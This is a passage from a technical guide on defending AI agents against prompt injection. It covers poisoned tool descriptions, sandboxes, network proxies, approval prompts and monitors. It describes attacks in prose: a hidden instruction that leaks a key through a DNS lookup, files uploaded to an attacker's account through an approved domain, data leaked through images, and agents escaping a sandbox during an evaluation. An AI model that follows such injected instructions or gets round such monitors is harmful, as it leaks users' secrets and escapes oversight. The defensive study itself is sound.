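and withholds the tool from the model if the fingerprint changes. Invariant Labs recommends this, together with fixing the version of the server. The protocol can notify clients of changes to the tool list, but these notices come from the server, so the client has to make its own comparison. The Model Context Protocol (2026) specification also lets the list depend on the caller's permissions, so the reviewer should look at the list that the assistant's own credentials produce.

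Pinning cannot help if the approved description was already malicious. It also doesn't stop a remote server from changing its code or results while the description stays the same.

A developer can avoid some of the risk by writing a new description of the tool. For `translate`, the maintainer could write "Translates a text into English" and rewrite the parameter descriptions. The company's descriptions then never reach the model, but the translations it returns still do.

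Tool annotations need separate checking. According to the Model Context Protocol blog (2026), a tool without annotations counts as potentially destructive, but clients differ in how strictly they apply this default. A hostile server can also declare a tool read-only and then delete data. A policy that exempts read-only tools from checks should therefore rely on the developer's own classification rather than the server's annotations.

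A registry is a catalogue of servers. Stacklok's *Tool annotations are becoming the risk vocabulary for agentic systems* argues that annotations become reliable if a registry has compared them with the source code. The value of a registry therefore depends on what its operators check. A digital signature shows who published a server and that nobody has altered it since, but not that the publisher is honest. The attacker in the WhatsApp demonstration, for example, could have signed both descriptions.

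### Planning without the suspect description

In *Think Twice Before You Act*, Shi, Wang and colleagues (2026) present Tool-Guard, which reduces the influence of one tool's description on the use of another. They built it after finding that existing defences, including repeated requests, tool filters and Progent, failed to stop many attacks that exploit this influence.

Suppose the description of `translate` contains a false rule that the agent must read `.env` before commenting. Tool-Guard would work as follows:

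1. The planning model sees all the tools and proposes `read_file(".env")`.
2. One model checks whether the call fits the user's request and the earlier calls. Another checks whether its arguments come from the request or from earlier results. Neither reads the tool descriptions.
3. The call fails a check, so the software moves `read_file` to a separate list. This list holds tools that another description may have influenced, so `read_file` itself is not under suspicion.
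4. The software asks the planning model for the next step twice, once with each list. When the model considers `read_file`, it no longer sees the description of `translate`.
5. The software picks one of the proposed calls and checks it again before running it.

The software splits the full set of tools into two groups, with no tool in both, and plans separately with each group's tool descriptions. Every tool remains available, so the agent can still do its work. For MCP, the software can group tools by server instead.

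In five repeated runs on AgentDojo, average attack success with Tool-Guard was between 0.40% and 1.54% on three models. In tests with GPT-4o, the researchers removed parts of the system to measure their contribution:

| System | Attack success | Utility without attacks | Utility under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tool-Guard | 2.06% | 72.16% | 58.76% |
| Checks only | 2.06% | 55.67% | 26.80% |
| Checks, with influenced tools hidden | 3.09% | 62.89% | 41.23% |

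The checks provide most of the security, and separate planning mainly keeps the agent useful. Tool-Guard used about 1.45 times as many tokens as an undefended agent and took about 3.7 times as long.

The researchers also tried five adaptive attacks on GPT-4o-mini. The most effective, which used a model to refine the descriptions repeatedly, succeeded 15.45% of the time without Tool-Guard and 2.06% with it. The other four never succeeded against Tool-Guard. These results are encouraging, but the undefended agent already resisted most of the attacks, and both models are old. The test also assumed that poisoned tools otherwise work normally. A hostile server could also put text in its results, and the model that checks arguments reads those results.

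### A checklist for admitting a new tool

The maintainer can go through these questions before connecting any third-party tool. The right-hand column gives acceptable answers for `translate`.

| Question | Acceptable answer for `translate` |
|---|---|
| Does the agent need it, and does anyone still maintain it? | Some reports are in Japanese, and the company still fixes security flaws |
| What will the supplier receive? | Only the text of public issues, which a rule on the arguments enforces |
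| Who can influence what it returns? | The supplier and whoever wrote the issue, so the result is untrusted |
| Has a person read the full description, the parameters and any bundled instructions? | Yes, and the model sees the maintainer's own version |
| What happens if the definition changes? | The client withholds the tool until the maintainer has reviewed it |
| Do the rules name the server as well as the tool? | Yes, because two servers may use the same tool name |
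| Whose authority does it use? | A key that works only for translation, with no access to GitHub |
| Where is the credential? | In the client's protected storage, outside the context and any file the agent can open |
| Does the server reject callers without valid credentials? | Yes, the maintainer has tested this |
| What becomes possible in combination with the other tools? | If the agent can open secret files, `translate` is another way for their contents to leave, so it runs in a separate session |
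| How can the maintainer remove it? | By revoking the key and deleting the connection |

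## Confining what tools can reach

Suppose the maintainer wants the triage assistant to reproduce crashes, and gives it a fifth tool, `run_command`, which runs a command on the assistant's machine. The reporter of issue 412 has attached a short script that triggers the crash, and the model requests `run_command("python repro.py")`. The policy layer can check the command's text against its rules, but that text doesn't show what the script will do. The script could open `.env`, rewrite the build scripts and connect to a stranger's server, all within one permitted call. Browsers and code interpreters pose the same problem, because a click's effect depends on the page and a program's effect depends on its code.

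More detailed rules about commands help only a little. According to lecture slides from UT Austin, such rules govern tool calls but not the processes those calls start. The slides describe command-blocking patterns as guardrails against accidents. Stopping a hostile script requires confinement, meaning limits that the operating system or network imposes on every process, however it started.

### A name lookup that leaked a key

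The `ping` leak in Claude Code came from a built-in list of commands that ran without approval because they seemed safe. Embrace The Red's *Claude Code* describes how Johann Rehberger found this list in the program's code and had Claude search it for commands that could send data out. The search turned up `ping`, `nslookup`, `host` and `dig`.

All four commands look up the network address for a server's name. A request for `abc.example.com` eventually reaches the name server responsible for `example.com`, so whoever runs that server can read every name that people look up under that domain. In Rehberger's test, a hidden instruction in a source file made the model take a key from `.env`, put it in front of a domain name he controlled, and run `ping` on the result, and the lookup alone was enough to send him the key.

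Rehberger reported the flaw on 26 May 2025, and Anthropic had fixed it by 6 June. The security advisory, OSV's *GHSA-x5gv-jw7f-j6xj* (2025), rates it 7.1 (high) and attributes it to an overly broad list of safe commands. Rehberger had proposed removing the four commands from the list, so that the user would have to approve them.

That closes the known routes, but a package installer, a test suite or `repro.py` can also look up a name. To approve a command safely, a developer has to know everything the program can do with any arguments, including what other programs it may start. Limiting destinations doesn't require this knowledge, because the limit applies to the connection itself. This rule would have closed the channel:

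```
Processes the agent starts have no network access,
including name lookups, except through a proxy
that connects only to approved hosts.
```

Docker, a common container system, can run a container without any network, and Anthropic's deployment guide confirms that name lookups then fail inside it. The proxy runs outside the container and looks up approved names itself. With this rule, `ping` could have stayed on the list. The rule needs to mention lookups explicitly. Zenity Labs' *It's Always DNS in Claude’s Sandbox*, for example, describes a sandbox whose proxy correctly blocked web traffic while name lookups still got out.

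### Limiting file access

An operating system can restrict which files a process and its child processes may open. Claude Code's current sandbox does this with bubblewrap on Linux and Seatbelt on macOS. By default, a sandboxed command can write only to the project folder, a temporary folder and any folders the user has added. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports that the sandbox reduced permission prompts by 84%, because commands inside it can mostly run without approval.

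File limits do not protect what is inside the permitted folders. If the triage assistant gets read-only access to the whole repository, `repro.py` can read `.env`, so the maintainer has to exclude that file from the assistant's access. If the assistant needs to write, an overlay file system can store its changes in a separate layer, so the maintainer can inspect the changes before applying or discarding them. The software must also resolve symbolic links (files that point to other files) before it checks a path, because a link in a permitted folder could lead outside it.

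File and network limits depend on each other. A script with unrestricted network access can send out everything it can read. If only its network access is limited, it can still change a startup file or the agent's own settings, and a later program may then run commands the script planted there, outside the sandbox.

Developers also need to check which parts of an agent a sandbox covers. According to Anthropic's documentation, Claude Code's built-in sandbox is off by default and covers only shell commands. The file tools, local MCP servers and hooks (commands that run automatically at certain moments) run outside it. When a command fails in the sandbox, Claude may retry it outside, usually after an approval, unless the user turns this option off. Running the whole agent inside a container or virtual machine puts all these parts behind one boundary.

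The boundary must be in place before the agent opens the project. Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received three reports of attacks that ran code before the user had agreed to anything. In the simplest, a cloned repository contained a settings file with a hook, and Claude Code ran the hook before asking whether the user trusted the folder.

### Isolating processes

A hostile program may also attack the operating system's kernel, the core that controls files, memory and devices for all other programs. The usual forms of isolation differ mainly in what the program would have to break to escape.

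| Boundary | How it works | What an escape requires |
|---|---|---|
| Container | The program gets its own view of files, processes and the network but shares the host's kernel | A flaw in the host's kernel |
| gVisor | A second, smaller kernel runs as an ordinary program and handles most of the container's requests | A flaw in gVisor, and usually another in the host's kernel |
| Small virtual machine | The program runs on its own kernel and simulated hardware | A flaw in the software that runs the virtual machine or simulates its devices |

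The stronger boundaries now require fairly little time and memory. Firecracker, which runs small virtual machines, starts one in under 125 milliseconds and adds less than 5 MiB of memory, so the maintainer could use a fresh machine for every issue.

None of the three protects what the developer deliberately makes available inside it. A virtual machine with a writable copy of the repository and an open internet connection protects the host but leaves the code and `.env` exposed. Isolation can also hide an attack from defenders. When companies evaluated Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent for office work, their security software could not inspect the virtual machine that Cowork ran in. Anthropic now lets administrators export event logs, but this is slower than live monitoring.

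### Limiting network destinations

The container or virtual machine usually has only one network connection, a private link to a proxy on the host machine. The proxy allows connections only to servers on a list. This stops `repro.py` from sending the project's passwords to an unlisted server.

The script can still send data to any approved host. Claude Cowork's proxy approved `api.anthropic.com` because the product cannot work without it. A security researcher showed that a malicious file in the user's folder could supply hidden instructions and an attacker's key for that service. Claude then uploaded the user's files to the attacker's Anthropic account, and the proxy allowed the request because the destination was on the list. Anthropic concluded that approving a domain gives access to every function the domain offers. The triage assistant has the same exposure if the maintainer approves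 GitHub's servers, where an attacker can easily have an account.

Anthropic fixed the leak with a proxy that passes only requests carrying the virtual machine's own session token. It also noted that gVisor and the virtual machine software had been reliable, but the proxy it had written itself had failed.

A proxy has to decrypt traffic to check more than the host name. A proxy that doesn't decrypt relies on the name the program supplies, so a program can sometimes name an approved host and reach another one that shares its infrastructure. A decrypting proxy can enforce narrower rules, such as allowing new comments only under issue 412. The developer has to install the proxy's certificate inside the sandbox so that programs accept it. Some programs ignore proxy settings, so the sandbox should either have no other route out or redirect all traffic to the proxy.

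### Keeping credentials outside

The same proxy can hold the GitHub token and add it to approved requests. Code in the sandbox then never has the token, so a stranger's script cannot steal it for later use. The script can still misuse the token by sending requests through the proxy while the assistant runs, so the token's permissions should stay narrow.

Limits on what tools can reach matter even with a well-trained model. In a February 2026 test at Anthropic, a researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt that looked like routine work but included a step to read the employee's cloud credentials and send them to an outside server. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. Defences that compare an action with the user's request could not detect the attack, because the instruction came from the user. Anthropic considers limits on the environment the only defence that works in such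 a case. Those limits would have kept the credentials file out of reach and blocked the outgoing request.

### What each level can observe

Confinement rules refer to files and connections because the operating system has no other information. It can record that a process changed `src/loader.py` and contacted GitHub, but not whether this was part of triaging issue 412. The agent framework has the maintainer's request and the call `run_command("python repro.py")`, but no record of the files the script opened.

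*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls this mismatch a semantic gap and contrasts agents with web browsers. The operating system controls which folders the browser may write to, while the browser, which keeps track of websites, controls which site receives which cookie. Each layer enforces the rules it has the information for. An agent turns a request in everyday language directly into low-level actions, with no intermediate layers to enforce such rules.

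An ordinary sandbox cannot enforce many rules that matter to a business. Zhou and colleagues give the example of a rule that customer A's data must never go to customer B. If the agent is allowed to read both customers' files and write to both accounts, every file access and connection looks legitimate.

### Kairos

*KAIROS* (Hempel, Loose et al., October 2026) presents a system that checks an agent's effects at the sandbox boundary but uses the task to decide unclear cases. It works with unmodified agents, including closed-source ones. The agent runs in a small virtual machine, and everything it does to the project folder or the network passes through a monitor on the host. Tool calls and scripts written by the agent both reach the monitor as file operations and requests, so the monitor doesn't distinguish between them.

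The developer writes a short policy that lists trusted sources, sensitive data and the destinations that may receive it. For each effect *e*, such as a file write or a request, the monitor decides as follows:

- refuse, if a rule forbids *e*
- release, if the values that steer *e* come from trusted sources and ℓ(*e*) ⊑ clearance(target)
- defer, otherwise

The steering values are those that determine what the effect does, such as a recipient or a command. ℓ(*e*) is the highest sensitivity of any known secret in *e*, and the clearance is the highest sensitivity that the target may receive.

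The monitor can defer an action while it waits for more evidence. It applies a deferred file write to a separate copy that only the agent uses. If a request would change something elsewhere, the monitor holds it back and gives the agent a stand-in reply so that the agent can continue. The monitor cannot defer a request that fetches data, because the agent needs the answer, so it must decide immediately whether to send the request.

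A decision oracle, which can be a person or a second model without tools, then decides whether to allow each deferred effect. It receives the user's task, the record of what the agent did, and the origin of each value. The oracle cannot override a refusal, and the monitor treats an unreadable answer as a refusal.

For example, a setup guide written by an attacker tells the agent to install a script that runs at every commit (each time the agent saves a version of the code). Such scripts are common, so blocking them all would break legitimate work. The monitor defers the write, and the agent continues. When the agent makes a commit, the script runs and tries to send out a private key, which the policy blocks. The oracle then uses this attempt as evidence and discards the script before it reaches the real project.

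Hempel and colleagues compared Kairos with other defences on AgentDojo, using GPT-4.1 as the agent.

| System | Attack success | Utility without attacks | Utility under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 47.0% | 82.7% | 59.8% |
| Progent | 11.5% | 78.2% | 57.6% |
| CaMeL | 0.2% | 38.0% | 40.7% |
| Kairos | 2.7% | 85.1% | 69.5% |

The 2.4-point difference in utility without attacks is about two tasks in a single run, so Kairos probably did not make the agent better at its tasks. The gain under attack is larger. An agent that follows an injection often abandons the user's task, and Kairos has it continue that task after refusing the injected action.

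The policy provides most of the security. When the researchers refused every deferred effect instead of consulting the oracle, attack success did not measurably change, but utility without attacks fell to 42.7%. The oracle therefore mainly lets legitimate work proceed. In the runs without attacks, it wrongly refused only one effect.

On AgentDyn, a benchmark of open-ended tasks, Kairos reduced attack success from 37.8% without a defence to 1.7%. It also reduced utility under attack from 55.5% to 37.1%, because later steps often depended on effects that the monitor was holding. On AutoDojo, where a model rewrites each injection over six rounds, 8.8% of attacks succeeded with Kairos and 52.4% without a defence. Progent's published rate on AutoDojo is 7.7%, which is too close to Kairos's to show which defence is better. The attacks that worked against Kairos targeted tasks in which the user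 tells the agent to follow a document, and the oracle treated the attacker's text as what the user wanted.

These benchmarks simulate their tools in memory, so they have no files or network connections to monitor. The researchers wrote an adapter that turned each simulated tool call into an event for Kairos. The events still included the tool's name and arguments, which a real boundary would not provide. The results are good evidence for the policy and the oracle, but they hardly test whether Kairos can reconstruct what an agent is doing from raw file operations and requests.

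The virtual machine and proxy add little delay, about 1.9 milliseconds per file operation and 1.2 milliseconds per request. Consulting the oracle raised token use by 17.7% without attacks and 33.6% under attack.

Kairos has several other limits:

- It traces values by comparing text. If the agent encodes a secret before sending it, the monitor no longer recognises it and may release it to a trusted destination.
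- A file's sensitivity is lost if the agent moves the contents to another file before reading them.
- The oracle reads untrusted text as evidence, so it has the same weakness as other models that judge calls. The automated attacker on AutoDojo learned only whether each attempt succeeded, and one who knows the oracle could do better.
- The design does not cover escapes from the virtual machine, covert channels or harmful text in the agent's reply.
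- The prototype leaves the agent's own credentials inside the virtual machine, in files that the monitor does not check.

### Whether confinement can hold capable models

Critics object that a sufficiently capable model will find a weakness in whatever confines it. Anthropic has seen Claude models escape a sandbox simply to finish a task. In the OpenAI–Hugging Face incident, a shared service inside the boundary gave agents under evaluation internet access that the network rules were meant to block (OpenAI, *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead*, 2026).

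*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* argues that the network rules lacked complete mediation. They covered the agents' direct connections but not the requests that the service could make for them. A service that can reach the internet is part of the network boundary, so its outgoing requests need the same checks as the agents' own. If several agents can write to the service, they can also use it to communicate with each other, so each run needs separate or read-only storage.

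According to its technical report, OpenAI is isolating, restricting or replacing the services that high-risk agents can reach. It also requires these agents to run in virtual machines, with one set of network controls at the sandbox and an independent set around the wider cluster. The aim is to stop an attacker who breaks one service or sandbox from getting out.

The incident shows that capable agents can find and exploit an indirect route without an outside attacker. It is weaker evidence of how often agents in ordinary products would try, because the agents in the evaluation had instructions to exploit software and ran with reduced safeguards. OpenAI later found that its production instructions and software could make models more than 100 times less likely to compromise infrastructure in the same evaluation.

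The incident does not show that confinement is hopeless, since the agents got out through a service that had more access than its job required. But the objection is partly right, because OpenAI had tested this sandbox beforehand and the agents still escaped by combining previously unknown flaws. Checking every route out leaves fewer places where such a flaw can help an agent escape, but it cannot prove that the remaining software has none.

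Developers can at least tighten a policy one permission at a time, because removing a permission never reopens a route that the policy had already closed if the enforcement works correctly. The triage assistant, for instance, may not need a package service. The maintainer can install the project's packages in the virtual machine's image before the assistant reads any issue, and then remove the connection to the service.

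## Involving the user: approvals and displayed output

A sandbox can stop the triage assistant from connecting to a stranger's server, but only the maintainer can decide whether a particular comment should be posted under issue 412. But an attacker who cannot get a tool call past the monitor may still persuade the maintainer to approve it, or to carry out the attack by hand.

An application should keep the user's instructions, its approval requests and its displayed results separate. If approval requests appear in the chat, the model can write text that looks like an approval request. The application should therefore show these requests in an area the model cannot write to, and accept answers only there. It also has to verify that a click came from the user, which Claude for Chrome failed to do for its built-in tasks.

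### Instructions that state their limits

People tend to describe what they want done and leave out what the agent must not touch. *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents* (Yang, Zhou and colleagues, 2026) measured the effect of these omissions on Claude Code, Codex and Qwen Code. In one task, the user asks the agent to delete old experiment files. The request doesn't mention ownership, and the agent proposes deleting somebody else's files, although the benchmark's answer key permits deleting only the user's own. Of the 143 out-of-scope actions recorded, 132 broke only rules that appeared neither in the request nor in any tool output.

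The researchers then added a statement to each request that named the permitted environment, owner and component or protected branches. In 384 new runs, no agent proposed an out-of-scope action. The share of tasks that ended in the correct state rose from 25% to 94% for Claude Code, from 34% to 99% for Codex and from 21% to 49% for Qwen Code. Real users would gain less, because these statements came from the answer key and the benchmark is deliberately ambiguous. But a limit such as "comment only on issue 412 and change no files" takes the maintainer a few seconds to write, and code can turn it into rules for the monitor.

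### What an approval prompt should show

When Microsoft's configuration blocks `post_comment` because the assistant has opened a file, the maintainer gets an approval prompt that names the tool and the label that caused the block. The tool and label are the same whether the comment quotes a line of source code or the passwords in `.env`. Microsoft acknowledges that these approvals are coarse.

A prompt that relies on the model's own account is worse:

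```
The assistant would like to send the reporter the details
needed to diagnose the build failure.

[Allow]   [Always allow]
```

If the model is following an injection, the attacker has in effect written this text. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) includes an injection that tells a shopping assistant to post a one-star review and to report that it posted the five-star review the user wanted.

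Ordinary code can build a better prompt from the blocked call itself:

```
Post this comment?

Tool          post_comment
Destination   issue 412 (public: anyone can read it)
Account       yours
Full text     DB_PASSWORD=example-7731
Blocked       this run has opened a private file: .env
Undo          you can delete the comment, but not copies of it

[Don't post]   [Post this text once]   Expires in 5 minutes
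```

The model wrote only the comment's text, which appears in full because the maintainer has to judge it. The code should also make invisible characters and long gaps visible, since a row of spaces hid the stolen chats in the WhatsApp demonstration. The "Undo" line shows whether the user can reverse the action, following a suggestion in *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners.

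Commands are harder to present for approval. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) found that uninformative prompts, such as one showing only `python3 setup.py`, contributed to 31 of the 290 reports it analysed. To make the prompt for `python repro.py` more informative, the application could first run the script in an isolated copy without network access, then list the files it changed.

Some actions should never trigger an approval prompt. The maintainer has already decided that secrets must not appear in comments, so if the code detects text from `.env`, it should refuse the call without asking the user to approve it.

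### Binding the approval to the call

An approval is only as good as the match between what the user saw and what the application runs. The following procedure preserves that match:

1. Code stores the proposed call with every argument filled in and draws the prompt from the stored copy.
2. It computes a fingerprint of the call, the account and the contents of any file the call will run or send.
3. If the user approves, it saves the fingerprint with an expiry time.
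4. Just before execution, it computes the fingerprint again and runs the stored call only if

   H(call now) = H(call shown) ∧ now < expiry ∧ approval unused

5. It marks the approval as used in the same step, so that two requests cannot share it.

If the fingerprint left out the file contents, an agent could get approval for a harmless `repro.py` and then replace the script. The approval has an expiry time because circumstances can change too. For instance, a private repository may become public after the maintainer has approved a comment there.

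OpenAI's *Auto-review* documentation describes a similarly narrow approval in Codex. When the automatic reviewer denies an action, the user can approve that exact action for one retry in the same context, but the reviewer still checks the retry.

Refusals also need enforcement. *Let the Agent Do It?* points out that agents look for another path after a denial. Codex instructs the model not to seek the same outcome through a workaround, but only the monitor can reliably block workarounds.

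### How often people catch a harmful request

Anthropic reported in *How we built Claude Code auto mode* that users accepted 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts, and in *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026) that they accepted 97%. Most commands are harmless, so these rates alone do not show that users are careless.

Suppose a reviewer gets 100 approval requests a day, one of them harmful, and accepts all the harmless ones. An attentive reviewer catches 90% of harmful requests and a tired one catches 30%.

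| | Attentive | Tired |
|---|---|---|
| Chance of missing the day's harmful request | 10% | 70% |
| Expected misses in 20 working days | 2 | 14 |
| Chance of at least one miss in 5 working days | 41% | 99.8% |
| Share of prompts accepted | 99.1% | 99.7% |

The tired reviewer misses seven times as many harmful requests, but the acceptance rates are almost the same, so researchers have to measure attention by planting harmful requests and counting the rejections.

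In a study of 1,053 paid testers, Anthropic replaced one approval prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, rejected it. The rejection rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The testers worked in a test environment with nothing of their own at risk, and Anthropic used the study to support a change to its product. Developers protecting their own machines may well do better. But fatigue can explain only part of the problem, because most testers approved the command even early in a session.

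Many users also turn off some or all of the prompts. Anthropic reports that 62% of users had bypassed permissions or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands, and that a quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks off.

### Whether fewer prompts make people more careful

In the example above, an 84% cut in prompts, like the one from Claude Code's sandbox, would leave 16 a day. Let m be the share of harmful actions that now run without a prompt. If the reviewer becomes attentive again, the catch rate is

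0.9 × (1 − m)

which is better than the tired reviewer's 30% as long as m is below two thirds. The calculation depends on attention recovering, and there is little evidence that it does.

In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people without software backgrounds supervised a simulated assistant through 18 actions, 7 of which went beyond the user's request.

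| Who decides | Participants | Prompts per person | Unrequested actions blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user, for every action | 34 | 18.0 | 59.6% |
| A model, which passes doubtful actions to the user | 44 | 10.0 | 53.9% |
| The user's own standing rules | 35 | 10.9 | 39.6% |

Participants with standing rules saw fewer prompts but let more unrequested actions through. They could choose "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories, such as spending money, and chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules. When the assistant asked about an unrequested action, they approved it 66.8% of the time, compared with 40.3% for people who decided on every action. Yan cautions that the 66.8% figure covers only actions that participants had chosen to review. The 18-action session was also too short to show much fatigue. But the results give developers no reason to assume that people who see fewer prompts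 will read them more carefully.

### Three ways to ask less often

| Method | What it gives up |
|---|---|
| The user approves a plan once | Review of anything the plan leaves open, such as the text of a comment |
| The application asks only when a call violates a policy | Review of harmful actions that the policy allows |
| A second model decides | A predictable decision, and knowledge that only the user has |

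Users probably read a plan more closely than a single permission request, which is some reason to ask them to approve plans. Claude Code users reject 39% of plans but only 3% of single permission requests, although they may reject some plans for reasons unrelated to safety. Approving a plan restricts the agent only if the monitor enforces the plan and any change to it requires a new approval.

Asking the user only about violations removes most interruptions. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) gives an illustration based on OpenAI's internal use, in which 9,280 of 10,000 actions stayed inside the sandbox. The other 720 would have interrupted the user, and an automatic reviewer approved 713 of them. These prompts would therefore mostly be false alarms, and users could keep clicking "yes" out of habit. A misleading comment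 on issue 412, however, would not cause a prompt.

*How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026) examined five commercial agents and found that users often had to choose between frequent prompts and a model's opaque decisions. The Claude chatbot sometimes made such decisions even under the setting "Needs approval", for example by creating an email draft without asking. An application should therefore show whether the user, a rule or a model approved each action.

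### Letting a second model decide

In Claude Code's auto mode, a second model reviews the agent's actions. According to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), this is now the default mode on every plan. File reads and edits inside the project run without this review. For most other calls, the reviewer receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. The software removes the agent's explanations, which could mislead the reviewer, and the tool results, which could contain a prompt injection. A quick check flags doubtful calls, and the reviewer then reasons about them before deciding. If the reviewer blocks three calls in a row or 20 in a session, the software asks the user.

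In Anthropic's tests, this process wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 real tool calls. It missed 17% of 52 real actions in which an agent had overstepped its instructions, though with so few cases the true rate could be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the reviewer identified the danger but wrongly treated the user as having consented. For example, a request to "clean up the PR" does not authorise overwriting the project's history.

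The reviewer blocked 89% of the commands planted in the 1,053 sessions, far more than people did. The security firm Trajectory Labs also ran 720 injection attempts against three Claude models in auto mode, and none succeeded. That is weak evidence that the reviewer works, because on average only 0.09% of attempts succeeded with permission checks off.

Codex's reviewer does read tool results, which gives it more information but exposes it to hostile text. It caught 99.3% of OpenAI's synthetic injection cases and 90.3% of cases in which an agent went too far. Trębacz and colleagues report that testers could still mislead it into approving commands, and they do not expect such systems to provide firm guarantees.

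Results were far worse in the outside test by Yang and colleagues, on actions that broke unstated limits:

| Product | Out-of-scope actions approved | After adding the limits to the request |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 54% | 8% |
| Codex | 93% | 20–26% |
| Qwen Code | 80% | 20% |

The first column comes from the original runs, and the second from rechecking the same actions. These actions looked like ordinary maintenance, unlike Anthropic's planted commands, which were clearly dangerous. A reviewing model can recognise a destructive command, but it cannot tell that a folder belongs to a colleague unless its input shows this. Using a stronger model did not solve the problem, as Codex's reviewer approved 77 of 84 out-of-scope actions with its usual model and 82 with a stronger one.

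Some errors remain even when the limits are stated. In one run, Codex's reviewer rated 30 actions low for authorisation and medium for risk, then approved 16 of them, usually because the effect seemed small or reversible. The maintainer could reasonably let a second model approve test commands inside the sandbox, but should personally review any change to the build scripts.

### Images and links in a reply

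Even if every tool call is safe, the reply on the screen can leak data. An image loads without a click, which is how the planted memory in ChatGPT sent out conversations. A link sends its address when the user clicks it, and some chat programs fetch links automatically to create previews. These rules close both channels:

- Display the model's output as text with basic formatting, and remove raw HTML and terminal control characters.
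- Load no images from other servers. If the reply needs images, ordinary code should supply them from the application's own server.
- Turn off automatic link previews.
- Make a link clickable only if ordinary code created its full address, such as the address of issue 412. Show all other addresses as plain text.
- Apply the rules in every version of the app, since OpenAI's first check protected only ChatGPT's website.

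A website can have the browser enforce the image rule by setting a Content Security Policy, which lists the sources from which a page may load content. The setting `img-src 'self'` blocks images from other servers even if the application's own filter misses one. It doesn't affect links that the user clicks, so those need a separate rule.

Fetching images through the application's server hides the user's network address from the attacker, but the request still sends the attacker any data in the image's address. Allowing only addresses that already appear in the issue also does not prevent leaks, because an attacker can list 36 images there, one for each letter and digit. The model can then display them in the order that spells out a password.

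### Text that persuades the user

Suppose the assistant's summary of issue 412 ends with "To confirm the bug, run this command in your terminal", followed by a command the attacker wrote. The reply contains no image or link. If the maintainer runs the command, it has the maintainer's full permissions and bypasses the monitor and the sandbox.

In *Are You Sure?*, Li, Dai and colleagues (2026) tested 303 people on attacks of this general kind. Each participant completed three realistic tasks with an assistant that the researchers had compromised. In one task, the assistant recommended a malicious software package. In another, a hidden note in a CV changed its ranking of job candidates.

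| Warning | Participants who noticed something unusual |
|---|---|
| A notice at the start | 8.6% |
| A reminder beside every reply | 20.0% |
| An alert that interrupts the task | 25.0% |

Interrupting people appears to help, but three quarters of them still noticed nothing. The alert also appeared when the output was suspicious, which a real application would first have to detect. The exact differences between the warnings are uncertain, because the paper describes three groups of about 100 people but reports results for groups of 183, 60 and 60. Li and colleagues also conclude that technical experts are more susceptible, but with the first warning 6.8% of experts and 9.6% of others noticed something, a gap that could easily be chance.

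No display rule can close this channel, because harmful advice has the same form as useful advice. A bug report may legitimately require the maintainer to run a command, and an assistant that could never influence the maintainer's actions would be little use.

The application can make the model's output easier to check. It can mark a summary as based on a stranger's text and show the original passage beside it. It can show a suggested command with a button that runs it in the sandbox. It should also report completed actions from the tools' own records, so that the maintainer reads the comment GitHub published instead of the model's description of it.

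## Testing whether the boundaries hold

A maintainer who has written rules, labelled the tools and set up a sandbox still needs two kinds of test to find out whether they work. An enforcement test checks whether the software outside the model follows its policy. An attack test checks whether the whole application, including a real model, resists hostile text and still does its job. People easily confuse the results. If an assistant withstands 600 injections, the model may have ignored them all, which would leave the enforcement software untested.

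### Putting the model under the attacker's control

In an enforcement test, a script replaces the model and requests whatever an attacker would want. *The Stochastic Deputy* (2026), which presents a way to keep different customers' data apart, likewise assumes that the attacker chooses every tool call and argument. Enforcement tests take little compute because they don't run a model.

In *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, Mellafe Zuvic (2026) tested LangChain, a library for building agents, with a scripted tool call to change a merchant's payout account to the attacker's in a simulated payment system. With LangChain's default settings the change went through, because the library checks that the tool exists and usually that the arguments have the right type, but not whether the account is allowed. LlamaIndex and Stripe's Agent Toolkit don't check argument values by default either. ScopeGate,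 a policy layer with a list of permitted accounts, refused the same call.

ScopeGate also had to withstand 48 disguised or malformed calls, with invisible characters, look-alike letters, wrong data types and odd amounts. These exposed a bug in an early version, which compared the payment with a ceiling. Programs use the special value NaN ("not a number") for undefined results, and any test of whether NaN is greater than something comes out false:

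```
refuse if amount > ceiling                                 # NaN gets through
allow only if finite(amount) and 0 <= amount <= ceiling    # NaN is refused
```

After the correction, ScopeGate refused all 48. A model then revised its requests over 40 rounds, using the reason for each refusal as feedback. It produced 29 unauthorised calls, and none got through. ScopeGate also allowed all ten harmless calls in a separate check, which matters because a monitor that refuses everything would pass the other tests.

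The tester should also break the monitor on purpose. *Parallax* (2026) describes a design that blocks an action whenever a check crashes, times out or returns something unreadable. It also describes an attack in which someone floods the system with doubtful requests until a model-based check has used up its daily limit, then sends a harmful one. A tester can simulate both the failed check and the exhausted limit in a few lines of code.

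### Looking for ways round the monitor

Scripted calls test only the route that passes through the monitor. Many developers protect tools by wrapping each one in a checking function. If they forget to wrap one, the action happens silently, as *Stop Means Stop* (2026) points out, so the logs show no error. The tester therefore has to start from each harmful effect and try every route to it. *Metis* (2026) similarly says the monitor's developers should state which routes it covers, since two tools with the same effect may pass through different checks.

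*Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (2026) lists such checks for each type of sink and withdraws its security claim for any route that remains open. Adapted to a developer's needs, they include:

| Sink | What the tester tries |
|---|---|
| Files | Writing through a helper program instead of the file tool |
| Commands | Passing outside text straight to the shell |
| Network | Contacting the same service with a different program |
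| Repository | Applying an approved change to another version of the code |
| Memory | Using a saved note that has lost its label |

A sandbox can force all network traffic through the monitor, but files, shared memory and messages between local programs need their own restrictions and tests.

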